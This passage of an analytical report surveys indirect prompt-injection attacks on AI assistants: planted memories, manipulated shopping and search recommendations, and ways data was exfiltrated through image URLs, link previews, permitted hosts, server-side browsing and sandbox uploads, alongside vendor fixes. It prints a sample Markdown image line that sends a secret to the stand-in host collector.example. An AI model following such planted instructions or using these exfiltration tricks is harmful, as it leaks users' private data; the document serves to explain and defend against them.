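The researchers take these attacks seriously partly because they believe users trust assistants. Tenable writes that users tend to trust ChatGPT and so may be more likely to click. Permiso argues that users' trust in the assistant carries over to a fake alert. Microsoft (2026), writing about companies that try to influence assistants' recommendations, says people do not always check an assistant's advice as they would a random website's. None of the three cites data for these claims.

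Criminal campaigns provide some indirect evidence. Huntress' *AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust* traces an infection to a search for how to clear disk space on a Mac. The results included shared ChatGPT and Grok conversations that looked like help, and running a command copied from one of them installed software that steals data. Kaspersky (2025) found a similar campaign in which paid search advertisements led to a shared conversation on ChatGPT's website, made to look like an installation guide for the Atlas browser. Neither case involved indirect prompt injection, since the attackers produced and shared the conversations themselves.

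In the Huntress case, someone ran a dangerous command found in an assistant's conversation, but the same person might also have run it from an ordinary help page, and a high place in the search results may have been a large part of why they trusted it. A proper comparison would show the same warning to randomly assigned groups in an assistant's summary, an email or a website, and count how many people in each group act on it. None of the reports on these attacks includes such an experiment, so the claim is plausible but they leave it untested. It could also be false in some settings, since some users would notice that an account alert is out of place at the end of a summary of a coding project.

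Permiso's point about QR codes is stronger because it doesn't depend on whether users trust ChatGPT. A desktop password manager cannot check a site that the user opens on a phone.

### Instructions saved to memory

A false answer usually affects one conversation, but an assistant's memory can make the effect last. By default, ChatGPT uses a memory tool to save notes about its user, such as their job or preferred style of reply. In every later conversation, the product adds these notes to the developer's hidden instructions (s). Text from a stranger's document (d) can therefore return as part of s, alongside the text that developers train models to give the most weight.

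Johann Rehberger's 2024 Embrace The Red post, *ChatGPT*, describes three ways to plant memories in the assistant. When he referred to a Google document in a chat, ChatGPT saved each line of a list planted in it as a separate memory. An uploaded image also worked. A web page failed at first, and he got it to work only a few times, by combining the memory request with another task or delaying it until a later message. He concluded that OpenAI had quietly added a defence to browsing but not to files and images. ChatGPT displayed a "Memory updated" notice, which the user could open to see the change. Rehberger could also plant dozens of memories at once or delete all of them.

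In one demonstration, Techzine reports, false memories led ChatGPT to treat its user as a 102-year-old who lived in the Matrix and believed the earth was flat. In another, described in Embrace The Red's *Sorry, ChatGPT Is Under Maintenance*, Rehberger planted a single memory about how the user liked questions answered, and ChatGPT then responded to every question with a maintenance notice until the user found and removed the memory.

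OpenAI closed Rehberger's May 2024 report as a "model safety issue" rather than a security vulnerability. The next month he sent a demonstration in which a planted memory made ChatGPT's Mac app send all later conversations to an attacker. OpenAI fixed the leak in September. But Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* reports that attackers could still plant false memories through websites and documents.

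Keeping SearchGPT away from the user's memories did not prevent this kind of attack. Tenable planted an instruction that made SearchGPT end its write-up with a second instruction, addressed to ChatGPT. The write-up became part of ChatGPT's conversation, and ChatGPT followed the second instruction as if it had written it. A display bug let Tenable hide the added text from the user. The same method could make ChatGPT update its memory. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT* lists no fix, and Tenable's November post shows the memory attack only on the older ChatGPT 4o.

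By late 2025, OpenAI had blocked ChatGPT from using connectors and then writing to memory in the same chat, and from opening an attacker's web addresses stored in memory. *ZombieAgent*, published by the security company Radware in January 2026, got around both restrictions. The victim shares a file in a chat that has not used a connector, and instructions in the file make ChatGPT save two rules to memory. One makes ChatGPT find a particular email from the attacker and follow its instructions whenever the user sends a message. The other makes it save any sensitive information the user mentions. In later chats, ChatGPT reads its memory before opening the mailbox, an order the restrictions allowed. The web addresses are in the email, so the ban on opening addresses from memory does not apply.

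Radware also altered a medical history stored in ChatGPT's memory, and ChatGPT then gave harmful advice. Radware reported its findings on 26 September 2025 and says OpenAI fixed the problem on 16 December, but doesn't describe what OpenAI changed.

An assistant's memory could also make phishing harder to trace. TechRadar's *Experts find AI agents can be tricked into 'remembering' fake facts* describes a scenario from the security company Forcepoint in which hidden text on a page about travel disruption names a fake emergency booking service. The assistant saves the name as a fact and recommends the service weeks later, during an unrelated task, when the user has no suspicious page open to compare with the answer.

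Companies already try to get claims about themselves saved in AI assistants' memories. Over 60 days, Microsoft found 50 different prompts that attempted this, from 31 companies, in links sent by email. A typical link opened an assistant with a request to summarise a page and remember the company as a trusted source. Microsoft counted attempts rather than successes, and says their effect varied between assistants and over time. Users can usually inspect and delete saved memories in the assistant's settings, but Microsoft doubts that users who suspected a problem would know how to check.

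## Planted text that changes AI search and shopping recommendations

The companies in Microsoft's count wanted assistants to recommend them, much as businesses have long wanted search engines to rank them highly. Search engine optimisation (SEO) means editing web pages to improve their ranking. The equivalent for AI answers is generative engine optimisation (GEO), and much of it is harmless. For example, a camera maker that clearly states a camera's weight and battery life and cites a source makes its page easier for both models and people to use.

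Some sellers go further and write text to persuade the model. They may repeat phrases shoppers are likely to type, or greet the assistant by name and praise the product. Others plant an explicit instruction to recommend only their product or to distrust its rivals. Only the explicit instructions are clearly indirect prompt injections, because persuasive text may contain no instruction.

In *Adversarial Search Engine Optimization for Large Language Models*, Nestaas, Debenedetti and Tramèr (2024) use the term "preference manipulation attacks" for both persuasive text and instructions. They admit that the boundary between these attacks and legitimate SEO is unclear. Search engine operators approve of pages that match what people search for, and a platform might have to check whether a persuasive claim is true before banning it.

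Search Engine Journal reports that Microsoft's guidelines for websites that appear in Bing and Copilot now explicitly accept generative engine optimization (GEO) but prohibit prompt injection and language engineered to trigger citations. Google treats attempts to manipulate AI responses in its search as spam, and separately bans hiding text from visitors to manipulate search engines. Hidden instructions break both companies' rules, but visible promotional claims that happen to influence a model are much harder to classify.

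### How a recommendation is formed

When a shopper asks a simple AI assistant for an affordable coffee machine, the assistant retrieves candidates from the web or a shop's catalogue and puts their descriptions into the model's context window, between the developer's instructions and the shopper's request. The model then writes a list, and the order in which it names the machines is their ranking, because no separate program scores them. Each seller controls only its own description, but the model reads them all together, so one description can affect the position of every machine.

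The attack works only if the assistant retrieves the seller's page, but the page need not rank near the top. Nestaas and colleagues asked Bing Copilot about popular topics and compared the pages it read with Bing's ordinary rankings. In half the searches, Copilot read at least one page ranked below tenth, too low to appear on the first page of results.

### The first experiments

Kumar and Lakkaraju tested this design in *Manipulating Large Language Models to Increase Product Visibility* (2024), using ten fictitious coffee machines and Llama-2, a model with public weights. They added a string of tokens to one machine's description, then used the model's weights to repeatedly swap in tokens that made the answer more likely to begin with that machine. The final string looked like gibberish.

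One target, the ColdBrew Master, cost $199 and almost never appeared when the user asked for something affordable. After 100 rounds of replacements, it was the top recommendation. But the researchers had kept the machines in the same order throughout. When they shuffled the list, the string improved the machine's rank in only about 40% of 200 trials and made no difference in most of the others. For a cheaper machine that usually came second, the string lowered its rank about as often as it raised it. Shuffling the list while computing the string made the string much more reliable for both machines.

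The experiment did not involve a live product. A shopper or a simple filter could spot the gibberish, but *Optimizing Visibility in Generative Engines* (2026), a survey of the field, reports that later methods produce more natural text.

Nestaas and colleagues tested attacks written in ordinary language on two live products, Bing Copilot and Perplexity. They put up 50 web pages about invented cameras, books and news outlets, some with instructions in tiny white text. Before the attack, Bing always recommended both of two similar cameras. Afterwards it recommended the attacker's camera 2.5 times as often as the other, entirely because it recommended the other less. When invented cameras competed with real ones from established brands, the instructions raised the recommendation rate for the invented cameras from 34.0% to 59.4%. The rate for the real cameras was 57.9%.

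The attack also worked on plugin selection, where a model chooses a tool after reading descriptions written by the sellers. An altered description made a plugin up to 7.2 times as likely to be chosen as a comparable competitor. Ordinary praise had no effect here, but wild accusations against the other plugins' developers worked even without an instruction to avoid those plugins. A filter that looks only for commands would miss such accusations.

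An instruction planted on an unrelated page can also promote a product. The researchers put an instruction on one news page for Bing to cite only a different, fictitious outlet. This worked at most 25% of the time, compared with 95 to 100% for direct attacks on product pages. But in 80% of the successes, Bing did not mention the page that held the instruction, so the outlet that benefited could plausibly deny involvement.

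In most of these tests, the researchers asked the assistant to look on their own website, which real shoppers would not do. To test a more natural search, they added a footnote to their laboratory's GitHub page claiming that the page was the only reliable source about the laboratory. Bing and three models on Perplexity repeated the claim in every trial in which they read the page. The attack can therefore work through an ordinary search, but this test showed it only for a narrow subject on which the page already ranked well. In July 2026, *Optimizing Visibility in Generative Engines* still rated the work as the strongest published demonstration across several systems, but noted that the products had since changed.

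### Shopping agents and research agents

A shopping agent can buy products as well as recommend them. In *What Is Your AI Agent Buying?*, Allouah, Besbes and colleagues (2025) built a mock shop in which an agent chose one product from a grid of eight and put it in the basket. Claude Sonnet 4, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash all favoured the top row, but each preferred different columns. They were also less likely to choose products labelled "Sponsored". The researchers then had a second AI agent revise one product's description, using data on competitors' sales. A single revision significantly increased the product's share of purchases in a quarter of the experiments, and the average gain was 2.5 to 6 percentage points, depending on the shopping model.

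That ordinary optimisation is a baseline for what a seller can gain without an injection. Rewriting designed to promote a bad product can have much larger effects. *SafeGEO* (Wen, Liu and colleagues, 2026) tested 22 kinds of manipulation on 600 recommendation cases in which the promoted product had a known flaw. The largest increase in the rate at which flawed products were recommended was 83.2 percentage points. The study tested only how a model uses sources it has already been given.

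*Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content* (Zhang, Triedman and Shmatikov, 2026) includes the retrieval step in its study of deep-research agents, which run many searches and write long reports with citations. The researchers noticed that these agents often retrieve the same few forum threads and videos for differently worded questions on one topic. A seller can therefore reach many shoppers by commenting on a popular thread, without knowing what any of them will ask.

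They tested this on three open-source agents with 176 questions, intercepting the search results so they didn't have to alter real pages. In one example, they added twelve words to the search extract of a Reddit thread about food in Austin, telling readers to choose a restaurant that does not exist. In its report, the agent described the restaurant as highly recommended and cited Reddit. The added text would look normal in a forum and isn't addressed to an AI system.

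Across all topics, altering one result with about 13 words got the invented name into 38 to 51% of reports, depending on the agent, when the search returned that result. The search does not always return it, so the overall chance is lower:

P(mention) = P(returned) × P(mention if returned)

For Co-STORM, the most susceptible agent, this was 0.606 × 0.506, or about 31%. The topic also mattered. Agents readily mentioned an invented roadside assistance firm but mostly left out an invented cryptocurrency.

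All three agents wrote with GPT-4o-mini, a small model that was already old in 2026, so newer models might do better or worse. Testing the attack on commercial agents would have required planting false text on the live web, so the researchers counted citations instead. They found that 12.1% of Gemini Deep Research's citations pointed to sites with user-written content, compared with 0.4% for OpenAI Deep Research. Gemini therefore looks more exposed, but citation counts can't establish whether the attack would work.

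Publicity about an early draft led to some evidence of real attempts. Moderators of a Reddit forum on medical supplements recognised that someone was targeting the forum and changed their rules. Zhang and colleagues then simulated the attack on 460 supplement questions, and one altered page led the agent to recommend a fake compound about 10% of the time.

Evidence from live assistants in 2026 is more limited. Ticong (2026), in *Google AI Search Manipulation Sparks New Spam Crackdown*, reports on a BBC investigation in which misleading pages influenced major chatbots and Google's AI Overviews, the summaries above its search results. False content can have this effect without any planted instruction, as with The Guardian's fake camera reviews.

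### Why every seller has a reason to inject

In a hypothetical example, sellers A and B offer similar cameras, and 100 shoppers ask an assistant which one to buy. The table uses invented figures to show how many shoppers the assistant sends to each seller.

| | B does not inject | B injects |
|---|---|---|
| **A does not inject** | A 45, B 45 | A 15, B 70 |
| **A injects** | A 70, B 15 | A 30, B 30 |

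A gains 25 shoppers by injecting if B does not inject, and 15 if B does. The same is true for B, so both inject and each ends up with 30 shoppers instead of 45. Economists call this a prisoner's dilemma. Shoppers also lose, because 40 of them get no recommendation and the rest get one that has little to do with the cameras.

In tests with four competing products on Bing and Perplexity, Nestaas and colleagues found that a seller could raise its recommendation rate by injecting text, no matter how many competitors were already doing so. But when all four injected, each did worse than if none had. Claude 3 Opus, running on Perplexity, often refused to recommend any product when it encountered several injections. The researchers measured recommendations, not sales, and controlled every page in the experiment.

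A penalty can deter sellers from injecting if the platform catches enough of them. Suppose the platform detects a share p of injections and sends those sellers no shoppers. If B is honest, A can expect 70(1 − p) shoppers from injecting and 45 from staying honest, so honesty brings A more shoppers once p exceeds about 36%. If B is already injecting and has escaped detection, A can expect 30(1 − p) shoppers from injecting and 15 from staying honest, so p has to exceed 50%. A platform that waits until injection is common therefore needs to catch more of it in this example. A long ban would lower both thresholds, because a caught seller would also lose future shoppers.

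### "Summarize with AI" buttons

The promotional links Microsoft reported in February 2026 (50 prompts from 31 companies) came from ordinary businesses, not criminals. The businesses spanned more than a dozen industries, including health and financial services, and one was a security vendor.

Many of the prompts were attached to a "Summarize with AI" button on a web page, which opens an assistant such as Copilot, ChatGPT or Claude with the request already filled in. In the most aggressive cases, companies tried to save whole passages of marketing copy, not just their names, in the assistant's memory.

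Microsoft traced the practice to free tools, including a code package called CiteMET. Promoters market these tools as a "growth hack" for getting cited by AI. A business can add such a button without knowing anything about prompt injection.

Microsoft's count probably misses many buttons because it covers only links that appeared in email. Microsoft also warns that many of these sites host comments, and an assistant that treats a site as trusted may give more weight to strangers' comments there.

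### Spam rules and their limits

Bing had a rule against prompt injection by July 2024. Search Engine Roundtable's *Prompt Injection Added To Bing Webmaster Guidelines* (2024) quotes the penalty as "demotion or even delisting". Microsoft expanded the rule into a full section in February 2026. Google updated its spam policies on 15 May 2026, and PPC Land's *Google spam policies now officially cover AI Overviews and AI Mode* (2026) points out that the update applied existing rules to AI answers and added no new ones. Google uses automated systems and some human review to find offenders, which may rank lower or disappear from its results.

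Neither the policies nor the experiments above show whether the penalties work. A test would have to plant comparable pages, record how many the platform caught, and check whether the rest still changed its answers. Microsoft says that in several cases it could no longer reproduce previously reported behaviour in Copilot, but this is the company's account of its own product, and it concerns attacks on the assistant's memory, not search rankings.

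A search penalty also falls on the site that hosts the planted text, which may not belong to the seller. Google is unlikely to delist Reddit over one comment about a restaurant. Lowering a site's rank also doesn't stop links sent by email. Google and Bing can't find planted text that a site shows only to OpenAI's crawler, as Tenable's site did.

Assistants could instead limit the influence of any one source. In one method, a model answers separately from each source and then takes a majority vote. Nestaas and colleagues think this could work for simple facts, but they doubt it would work for choosing between products, because each seller's page favours its own. Zhang and colleagues found that excluding all user-written pages stopped their attack but made the reports worse.

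*When Optimization Becomes Manipulation* (2026) proposes rating each source's reliability before deciding whether to cite it, using suspicious pages only as a fallback and removing high-risk ones. Its prompt has a language model rate the sources by reading the search results. A seller could write text to fool that model too, much as Marco Buono fooled an early injection checker in 2022.

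## How stolen data leaves the assistant

To steal private data, an attacker must get it from the assistant to a place where they can read it. This step isn't needed when a planted product page only has to change what the user reads. Many assistants have no tool for sending messages to strangers, so attackers use ordinary features instead, such as displaying images.

### An image address that carries a secret

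Suppose an assistant can read its user's mailbox, and one email there mentions a confidential project called Blue Heron. The attacker sends the user another email, with a hidden instruction to end any summary with an image and to put the project's name in the image's address. When the user asks for a summary of the day's mail, the model writes one in Markdown and adds this line:

`![ ](https://collector.example/dot.png?d=Blue%20Heron)`

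The exclamation mark and square brackets introduce an image, and the parentheses contain the address to load it from. The part after the question mark is a parameter, which is extra information for the server, and %20 stands for a space. The chat client (the web page or app that displays the conversation) turns the line into an image. To display it, the browser requests dot.png from collector.example, which belongs to the attacker. Websites commonly log the addresses that browsers request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains, so the attacker finds this in the log:

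`GET /dot.png?d=Blue%20Heron`

The request itself delivers the secret, so the server can return a one-pixel image or nothing, and the user sees an ordinary summary.

The leak works only if all of these conditions hold:

| Condition | Fix that removes it |
|---|---|
| The planted text and the private data are in the same context window | Keep outside text away from private data |
| The model follows the instruction and copies the data into an address | Train the model to resist, or filter what it reads and writes |
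| The client loads images automatically | Load outside images only after the user agrees, or never |
| The browser may contact the attacker's host | Restrict the hosts that images can come from |
| The attacker can read what that host receives | Permit only hosts where strangers cannot collect requests |

It is hard to keep private data and untrusted content away from an assistant that reads mail, so vendors tend to limit how data can leave by restricting how images load. Ordinary code can enforce such a rule whatever the model writes. Willison considers the ability to send data out generally the easiest part of his "lethal trifecta" to remove.

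Johann Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Microsoft stopped Bing Chat from loading such images that May. OpenAI added a check on image addresses in December but left it out of its Mac and iPhone apps. Rehberger also found ways around the check, which OpenAI tightened around August 2025. By then, researchers had found dozens of similar leaks in other companies' products.

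### Links and previews

A Markdown link is written like a Markdown image but without the exclamation mark. The browser displays the link's text and contacts the host only when the user clicks, so the attacker also has to make the link tempting. A product can remove suspicious links before it shows an answer. Glean, which sells an assistant for searching company data, lets administrators keep links that a trusted tool returned, that point to a trusted domain or that the user typed. The model generated the Blue Heron address itself, so the address would fail these checks unless collector.example were a trusted domain.

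Messaging apps can leak the data in a link without anyone clicking it. When someone posts a link in Slack, Discord or Telegram, the app fetches the page to show its title and a picture. The fetch sends the host the same address that a click would. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do*, passed on Rehberger's advice that developers can turn off these previews for messages their bots post in Slack.

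In *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, the security company PromptArmor reports that the problem also affected OpenClaw, an agent that people can message through Telegram. OpenClaw's replies produced link previews by default, so a link containing private data leaked that data as soon as the reply arrived. One line in OpenClaw's configuration file turns the previews off. PromptArmor wants messaging apps to offer this setting for individual chats so that previews still work in conversations between people.

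### Requests sent before the user approves

In January 2026, PromptArmor published weaknesses in Notion AI, IBM Bob, Superhuman and Claude Cowork. Notion AI is an assistant that can edit shared documents in Notion. In the test described in PromptArmor's *Notion AI*, a user uploaded a job applicant's CV containing a hidden instruction and asked the assistant for help updating a hiring tracker. The assistant put the tracker's text into a web address and inserted an image with that address into the page. This leaked the text despite a request for the user's approval.

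Notion warned the user about the outside site and asked whether to continue, but it had already saved the edit and the browser had requested the image. The attacker therefore received salary expectations and comments on candidates even if the user refused. Notion also has a model scan uploaded documents for malicious text. PromptArmor did not try to defeat this scanner because an attacker could instead use a web page or another source that Notion did not appear to scan. Notion changed how the assistant's edits work after the report reached its own team.

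IBM's coding agent, Bob, which was in closed beta at the time, had a related weakness in its editor. A data file can give the address of a schema, which describes the file's expected format, and Bob's editor downloaded schemas automatically. If the model put private data into that address, the download could send the data out before the user accepted the edit. PromptArmor's *IBM AI ('Bob') Downloads and Executes Malware* also lists leaks through images in chat answers and in Mermaid diagrams, which the editor draws from text descriptions. The article mainly demonstrates a malware attack and lists these leaks as further findings, without walking through a theft.

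### Permitted hosts

Web applications can limit which hosts a browser contacts by sending it a content security policy. This is a line in the HTTP headers that lists where the page may load images, scripts and other content from. With the following policy, a browser would load images from the application's own site and one other host, and would never request dot.png from collector.example:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' images.example`

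The browser enforces the content security policy, so the policy still applies when the model has followed a planted instruction. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3*, the standard for these policies, says they can reduce the harm from an injection but do not replace checks on input and output.

An allowlist, such as a content security policy, limits the web addresses that a product may contact or display content from. It usually identifies a host by name, which doesn't establish who will end up with the data. A permitted site may, for example, forward visitors elsewhere, which is how Tenable got past ChatGPT's link check. Browsers apply a content security policy to the forwarding address too, but they can't check requests that a permitted host's own server makes. EchoLeak and SearchLeak, two attacks on enterprise copilots (assistants that can read an organisation's mail and documents),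 got data out through permitted Microsoft hosts.

A permitted host may also let anyone collect data. The email program Superhuman blocked unknown hosts but allowed docs.google.com, which hosts Google's forms as well as its documents. Anyone can create a Google form and a link that submits an answer to it as soon as a browser opens the link. In PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, a planted email made Superhuman's assistant write such a link as an image address, with the text of other emails as the answer. When the browser requested the image, Google recorded the answer, which the form's creator could then read.

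In PromptArmor's attack on Superhuman, the user had only asked for a summary of recent mail and did not need to open the attacker's message. PromptArmor extracted the full contents of several emails in one response and parts of more than 40 in another. The same route later worked against OpenAI's Codex, which leaked legal and financial emails to a Google form in a test PromptArmor reported in April 2026. Superhuman and OpenAI have both fixed the flaws.

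Other products allowed hosts that were even easier to misuse. Bob's policy allowed storage.googleapis.com, where attackers can log requests. The default browser allowlist in Antigravity, Google's coding program, included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and see the requests sent to it. According to Willison, PromptArmor used webhook.site to show how a planted web page could steal a programmer's passwords for Amazon's cloud.

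### ForcedLeak

A domain can also change hands after a company has listed it as trusted. In 2025, Noma Security used an expired domain to take customer data out of Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents, in an attack it called ForcedLeak. The Hacker News (2025) reports a CVSS severity score of 9.4 out of 10 for the vulnerability.

Companies that use Salesforce can put a Web-to-Lead form on their websites or use it at trade shows. Each entry becomes a lead, the record of a possible customer, in the company's sales database. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reproduces Noma's account of how its researchers planted text in this form. They chose the description field because it accepts 42,000 characters, while the fields for names, company and email accept only 40 to 80. They filled it with what looked like a list of a possible customer's questions. In one item they asked for the email addresses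 of the company's leads, and in another they asked for an image whose URL included the answer.

The text does nothing until an employee uses Agentforce to process the lead. In Noma's test, the employee asked the agent to answer the lead's questions and draft an email with the results. Employees may well make such requests, but this one made the attack easier by directing the agent to the planted questions. Noma gives no success rate and doesn't report what happened when an employee asked only for a summary.

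Agentforce's content security policy permitted more than 20 hosts, including my-salesforce-cms.com, a domain Salesforce had let expire. Noma bought the domain for $5 and connected it to a server that logged every request. Because the policy still permitted the domain, the employee's browser loaded the image, and the leads' email addresses appeared in the log.

The list also permitted every address under amazonaws.com, where Amazon's customers can store files. An attacker might have used one of these addresses instead of the expired domain, though Noma doesn't report trying this. Salesforce recovered the domain, but that alone may not have been enough to stop the attack.

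From 8 September 2025, Salesforce also limited the web addresses its agents can output to a list that each customer's administrators control, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*. Administrators had to add every outside domain their agents needed or risk disruption. Agentforce Coworker, a related Salesforce product, removes web addresses by default. But Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses docs.google.com, the host used in the Superhuman attack, as its example of an address to add. A similar leak would still require Coworker to load images from that host automatically.

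### Web requests from the vendor's servers

A content security policy restricts the user's browser. It has no effect on an agent that opens web pages from its vendor's servers.

ChatGPT's Deep Research mode, an agent of this kind, spends 5 to 30 minutes reading websites and connected accounts before it writes a report. In the test in Radware's *ShadowLeak*, a user had connected Gmail and asked for research on the day's emails about a new employee. One email contained an instruction to find the employee's name and home address, add them to a URL and open it. Deep Research did this with its own browsing tool. The request went from OpenAI's servers to the attacker's server, so nothing appeared on the user's screen and the employer could not inspect the request on its network. Radware also found no sign that OpenAI's restrictions on image URLs applied to the browsing tool.

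Radware needed many attempts to make the attack work. Deep Research refused direct requests to send personal data, and it searched for the suspicious address online instead of opening it. Radware learned about the browsing tool by asking the agent what it could do, and refined the instruction using the parts of the agent's reasoning that ChatGPT displayed. The attack became reliable when Radware instructed the model to encode the data before sending it. According to Radware, the software carrying out the request then received only a harmless-looking string. This is plausible, but Radware could not inspect that software. Radware reports a 100% success rate for the final version but doesn't give the number of trials. OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August 2025.

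OpenAI then restricted ChatGPT to opening web addresses exactly as it had received them. Radware designed ZombieAgent, the attack that also planted lasting rules in ChatGPT's memory, to get around this restriction. The attacker's email supplies a ready-made address for each letter and digit. To send the word "heron", ChatGPT opens the addresses for h, e, r, o and n without changing them, and the attacker reads the word from the server's log.

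Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware prepared a separate set of addresses for each position in the secret. For a secret of up to b characters, the attacker needs:

26b + 10b = 36b addresses

A 12-character password would take 432 web addresses, plus a few more if it could contain spaces. Like ShadowLeak, ZombieAgent sent its requests from OpenAI's servers. Radware also used the channel to collect email addresses from the victim's inbox. The attacker's server then sent the same planted email to each of them.

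After ZombieAgent, OpenAI restricted the agent from opening links in emails unless they appeared in a public index, according to Particle.news' *Radware’s ‘ZombieAgent’ Bypasses ChatGPT Fixes, Forcing New OpenAI Restrictions*. OpenAI explained the wider rule in January 2026. A crawler with no access to conversations or accounts records addresses that are already public, and ChatGPT may open those automatically. For any other address, the agent has to try a different site or the user gets a warning. An address that contains Blue Heron is very unlikely to be in the index. OpenAI preferred this to a list of well-known sites partly because a list would cause frequent false alarms, and users would learn to click through warnings.

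The rule makes theft harder but still lets a patient attacker send data. Embrace The Red points out that a large website probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough to assign one to each letter and digit. With more pages, each request can carry more information. A 16-digit card number takes 16 requests if each page stands for one digit, but only four if the attacker has 10,000 pages, one for each possible group of four digits.

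Rehberger suggests preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, or having it reuse a stored copy of the page for a few minutes. Either would hamper an attacker who has one page per character, but wouldn't stop Radware's version with separate addresses for each position, because it uses each address only once. For that version, the attacker would first have to get all 432 pages for that password into OpenAI's index. Rehberger also warns that some OpenAI developers may not know about the check or use it in their products. The Codex leak three months later is consistent with this concern but doesn't establish that Codex lacked the check.

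Anthropic had similarly restricted Claude's tool for fetching web pages to addresses that the user had typed, that a search had returned, or that were linked from pages it had already fetched. In July 2026, Willison described how Ayush Paul exploited those links. Paul's site contained instructions for Claude to find its user's profile by following links letter by letter. Claude's path through the site revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic says it had already found the problem, and it has since stopped the tool from following links on fetched pages. This change also limits legitimate browsing, since people often reach a page through links on another one.

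### Search queries and domain-name lookups

An assistant that can search but cannot open pages may still leak data. In a 2023 mock-up, Greshake and colleagues tried to pass on a user's name through a search query. An ordinary query on a real search engine goes to the search company, whose logs the attacker normally cannot read, so the attacker needs a search tool that also contacts an address they choose.

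Abi Raghuram found such a weakness in Notion's agents in September 2025, a day after their release. Willison writes in *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents* that hidden text in a PDF made an agent read a list of clients, put their names and revenue into a web address and pass that address to the search tool. The Decoder's *Notion AI agents get security update after potential data leak* (2025) reports that Notion responded by improving its detection of planted instructions, including those in attached files. OpenAI says it applies its check on outgoing data to Deep Research's searches as well as to the pages it opens.

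Data can also leave through the domain name system (DNS), which a computer uses to look up a host's numeric address before connecting to it. The owner of a domain can run the server that answers lookups for every name under it. If an attacker owns collector.example and an agent's code looks up blue-heron.collector.example, the attacker learns the project name "blue-heron", even if a firewall then blocks the connection. Each part of a name can hold up to 63 characters, so a longer secret has to be split up. The vendor can close this channel by letting the agent's environment look up only permitted names.

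### Files uploaded from a code sandbox

Some agents write and run programs, usually in a sandbox, an isolated environment with limited access to files and the network. Claude Cowork is an agent for office work that Anthropic released as a research preview in January 2026. It runs code in a virtual machine (a simulated computer) that can contact only a few hosts. Two days after the release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that an attacker could steal a whole file through one of those hosts.

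In one attack, the victim gave Claude Cowork access to a folder of property documents and uploaded a Word file presented as a skill, a set of instructions for a particular kind of task. Tiny white text in the file made Claude run a command that uploaded the largest document it could find to Anthropic's file service. The sandbox allowed the connection because Anthropic's address was trusted, but the command used the attacker's account key, so the document went into the attacker's account. The document contained financial figures and partial social security numbers. Cowork never asked for approval.

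Skills are supposed to contain instructions, so Claude had some reason to follow the file. PromptArmor says the attack would also work with an ordinary document. Its main demonstration used Claude Haiku, Anthropic's small model. In a separate test, the stronger Opus 4.5 also leaked customer records when the text was planted in a software integration guide. PromptArmor gives no success rate for either model.

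Rehberger had reported the same flaw in Claude's chat product before Cowork existed, and Anthropic had acknowledged it without fixing it. After the new demonstration, Anthropic was updating Cowork's virtual machine, according to TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection*. A list of permitted hosts allows or blocks a whole service, whether the account on it is the victim's or the attacker's, so the sandbox would also have to check the account key and reject any that isn't the user's.

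An attacker can sometimes get a file through a download link, so the file itself doesn't have to be uploaded. Microsoft's OneDrive can create download links that work without a login and are short enough to fit in an image address. In May 2026, Willison reported an attack on Microsoft Copilot Cowork that used these links. The agent could email its own user without approval, and when the user opened the message, loading its images sent the links to the attacker.

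An employer that monitors its own network can detect some of these leaks but has little chance of noticing others:

| Channel | Who makes the request | Whether the user or employer can see it | Usual fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Image in an answer or document | The user's browser or app | The user sees a tiny or missing image at most; the employer can log the request | Block outside images or restrict their hosts |
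| Link | The user's browser, after a click | The user sees the link; the employer can log the request | Remove links without a trusted source |
| Link preview | The messaging service | The user sees the preview after the request; the employer usually sees nothing | Turn off previews for the agent's messages |
| Web page opened by a hosted agent | The vendor's servers | Usually neither, unless the product shows the agent's steps | Open only addresses already public, or ask the user |
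| Search query | The vendor's or search provider's servers | Only if the product shows its searches | Check outgoing queries and stop the search tool from opening arbitrary addresses |
| Domain-name lookup | The computer or sandbox running the code | The user sees nothing; the employer can log it if the code runs on its network | Look up only permitted names |
| Upload to a permitted service | The code sandbox | The user may find it in the command history; to the employer it can look like normal use | Check the account as well as the host |

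## Attack chains against enterprise copilots

Only employees can query an enterprise copilot, but outsiders can supply some of the text it reads. Microsoft 365 Copilot draws on the employee's mailbox, Teams chats, and files in OneDrive and SharePoint. Anyone who knows the employee's address can send them an email, and a supplier can share a document. Copilot then reads the outsider's text with the employee's permissions, alongside records the outsider can't open.

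Vendors use several controls to stop a planted email from leading to theft, so an attacker usually has to exploit several flaws in sequence, which security researchers call a chain.

An early attack, on Slack AI in August 2024, used a short chain. Slack AI answers questions from a company's Slack messages. PromptArmor posted an instruction in a public channel, and Slack AI retrieved it even for users who had never joined that channel. When a user asked about an access key stored in a private channel, the instruction made Slack AI include a link with the key in its address. The attacker needed an account in the company's Slack workspace, and the victim had to click the link. EchoLeak, reported to Microsoft five months later, required neither an account in the victim's organization nor a click.

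### EchoLeak, step by step

Aim Labs, Aim Security's research team, found the EchoLeak flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot. Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, gives it a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 in *CVE-2025-32711* (2025). *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives the researchers' own account.

Suppose an attacker sends an employee a long email that looks like a collection of staff guides. Some days later, the employee, who has not opened the email, discusses the confidential Blue Heron project with Copilot and then asks how to arrange a leave of absence.

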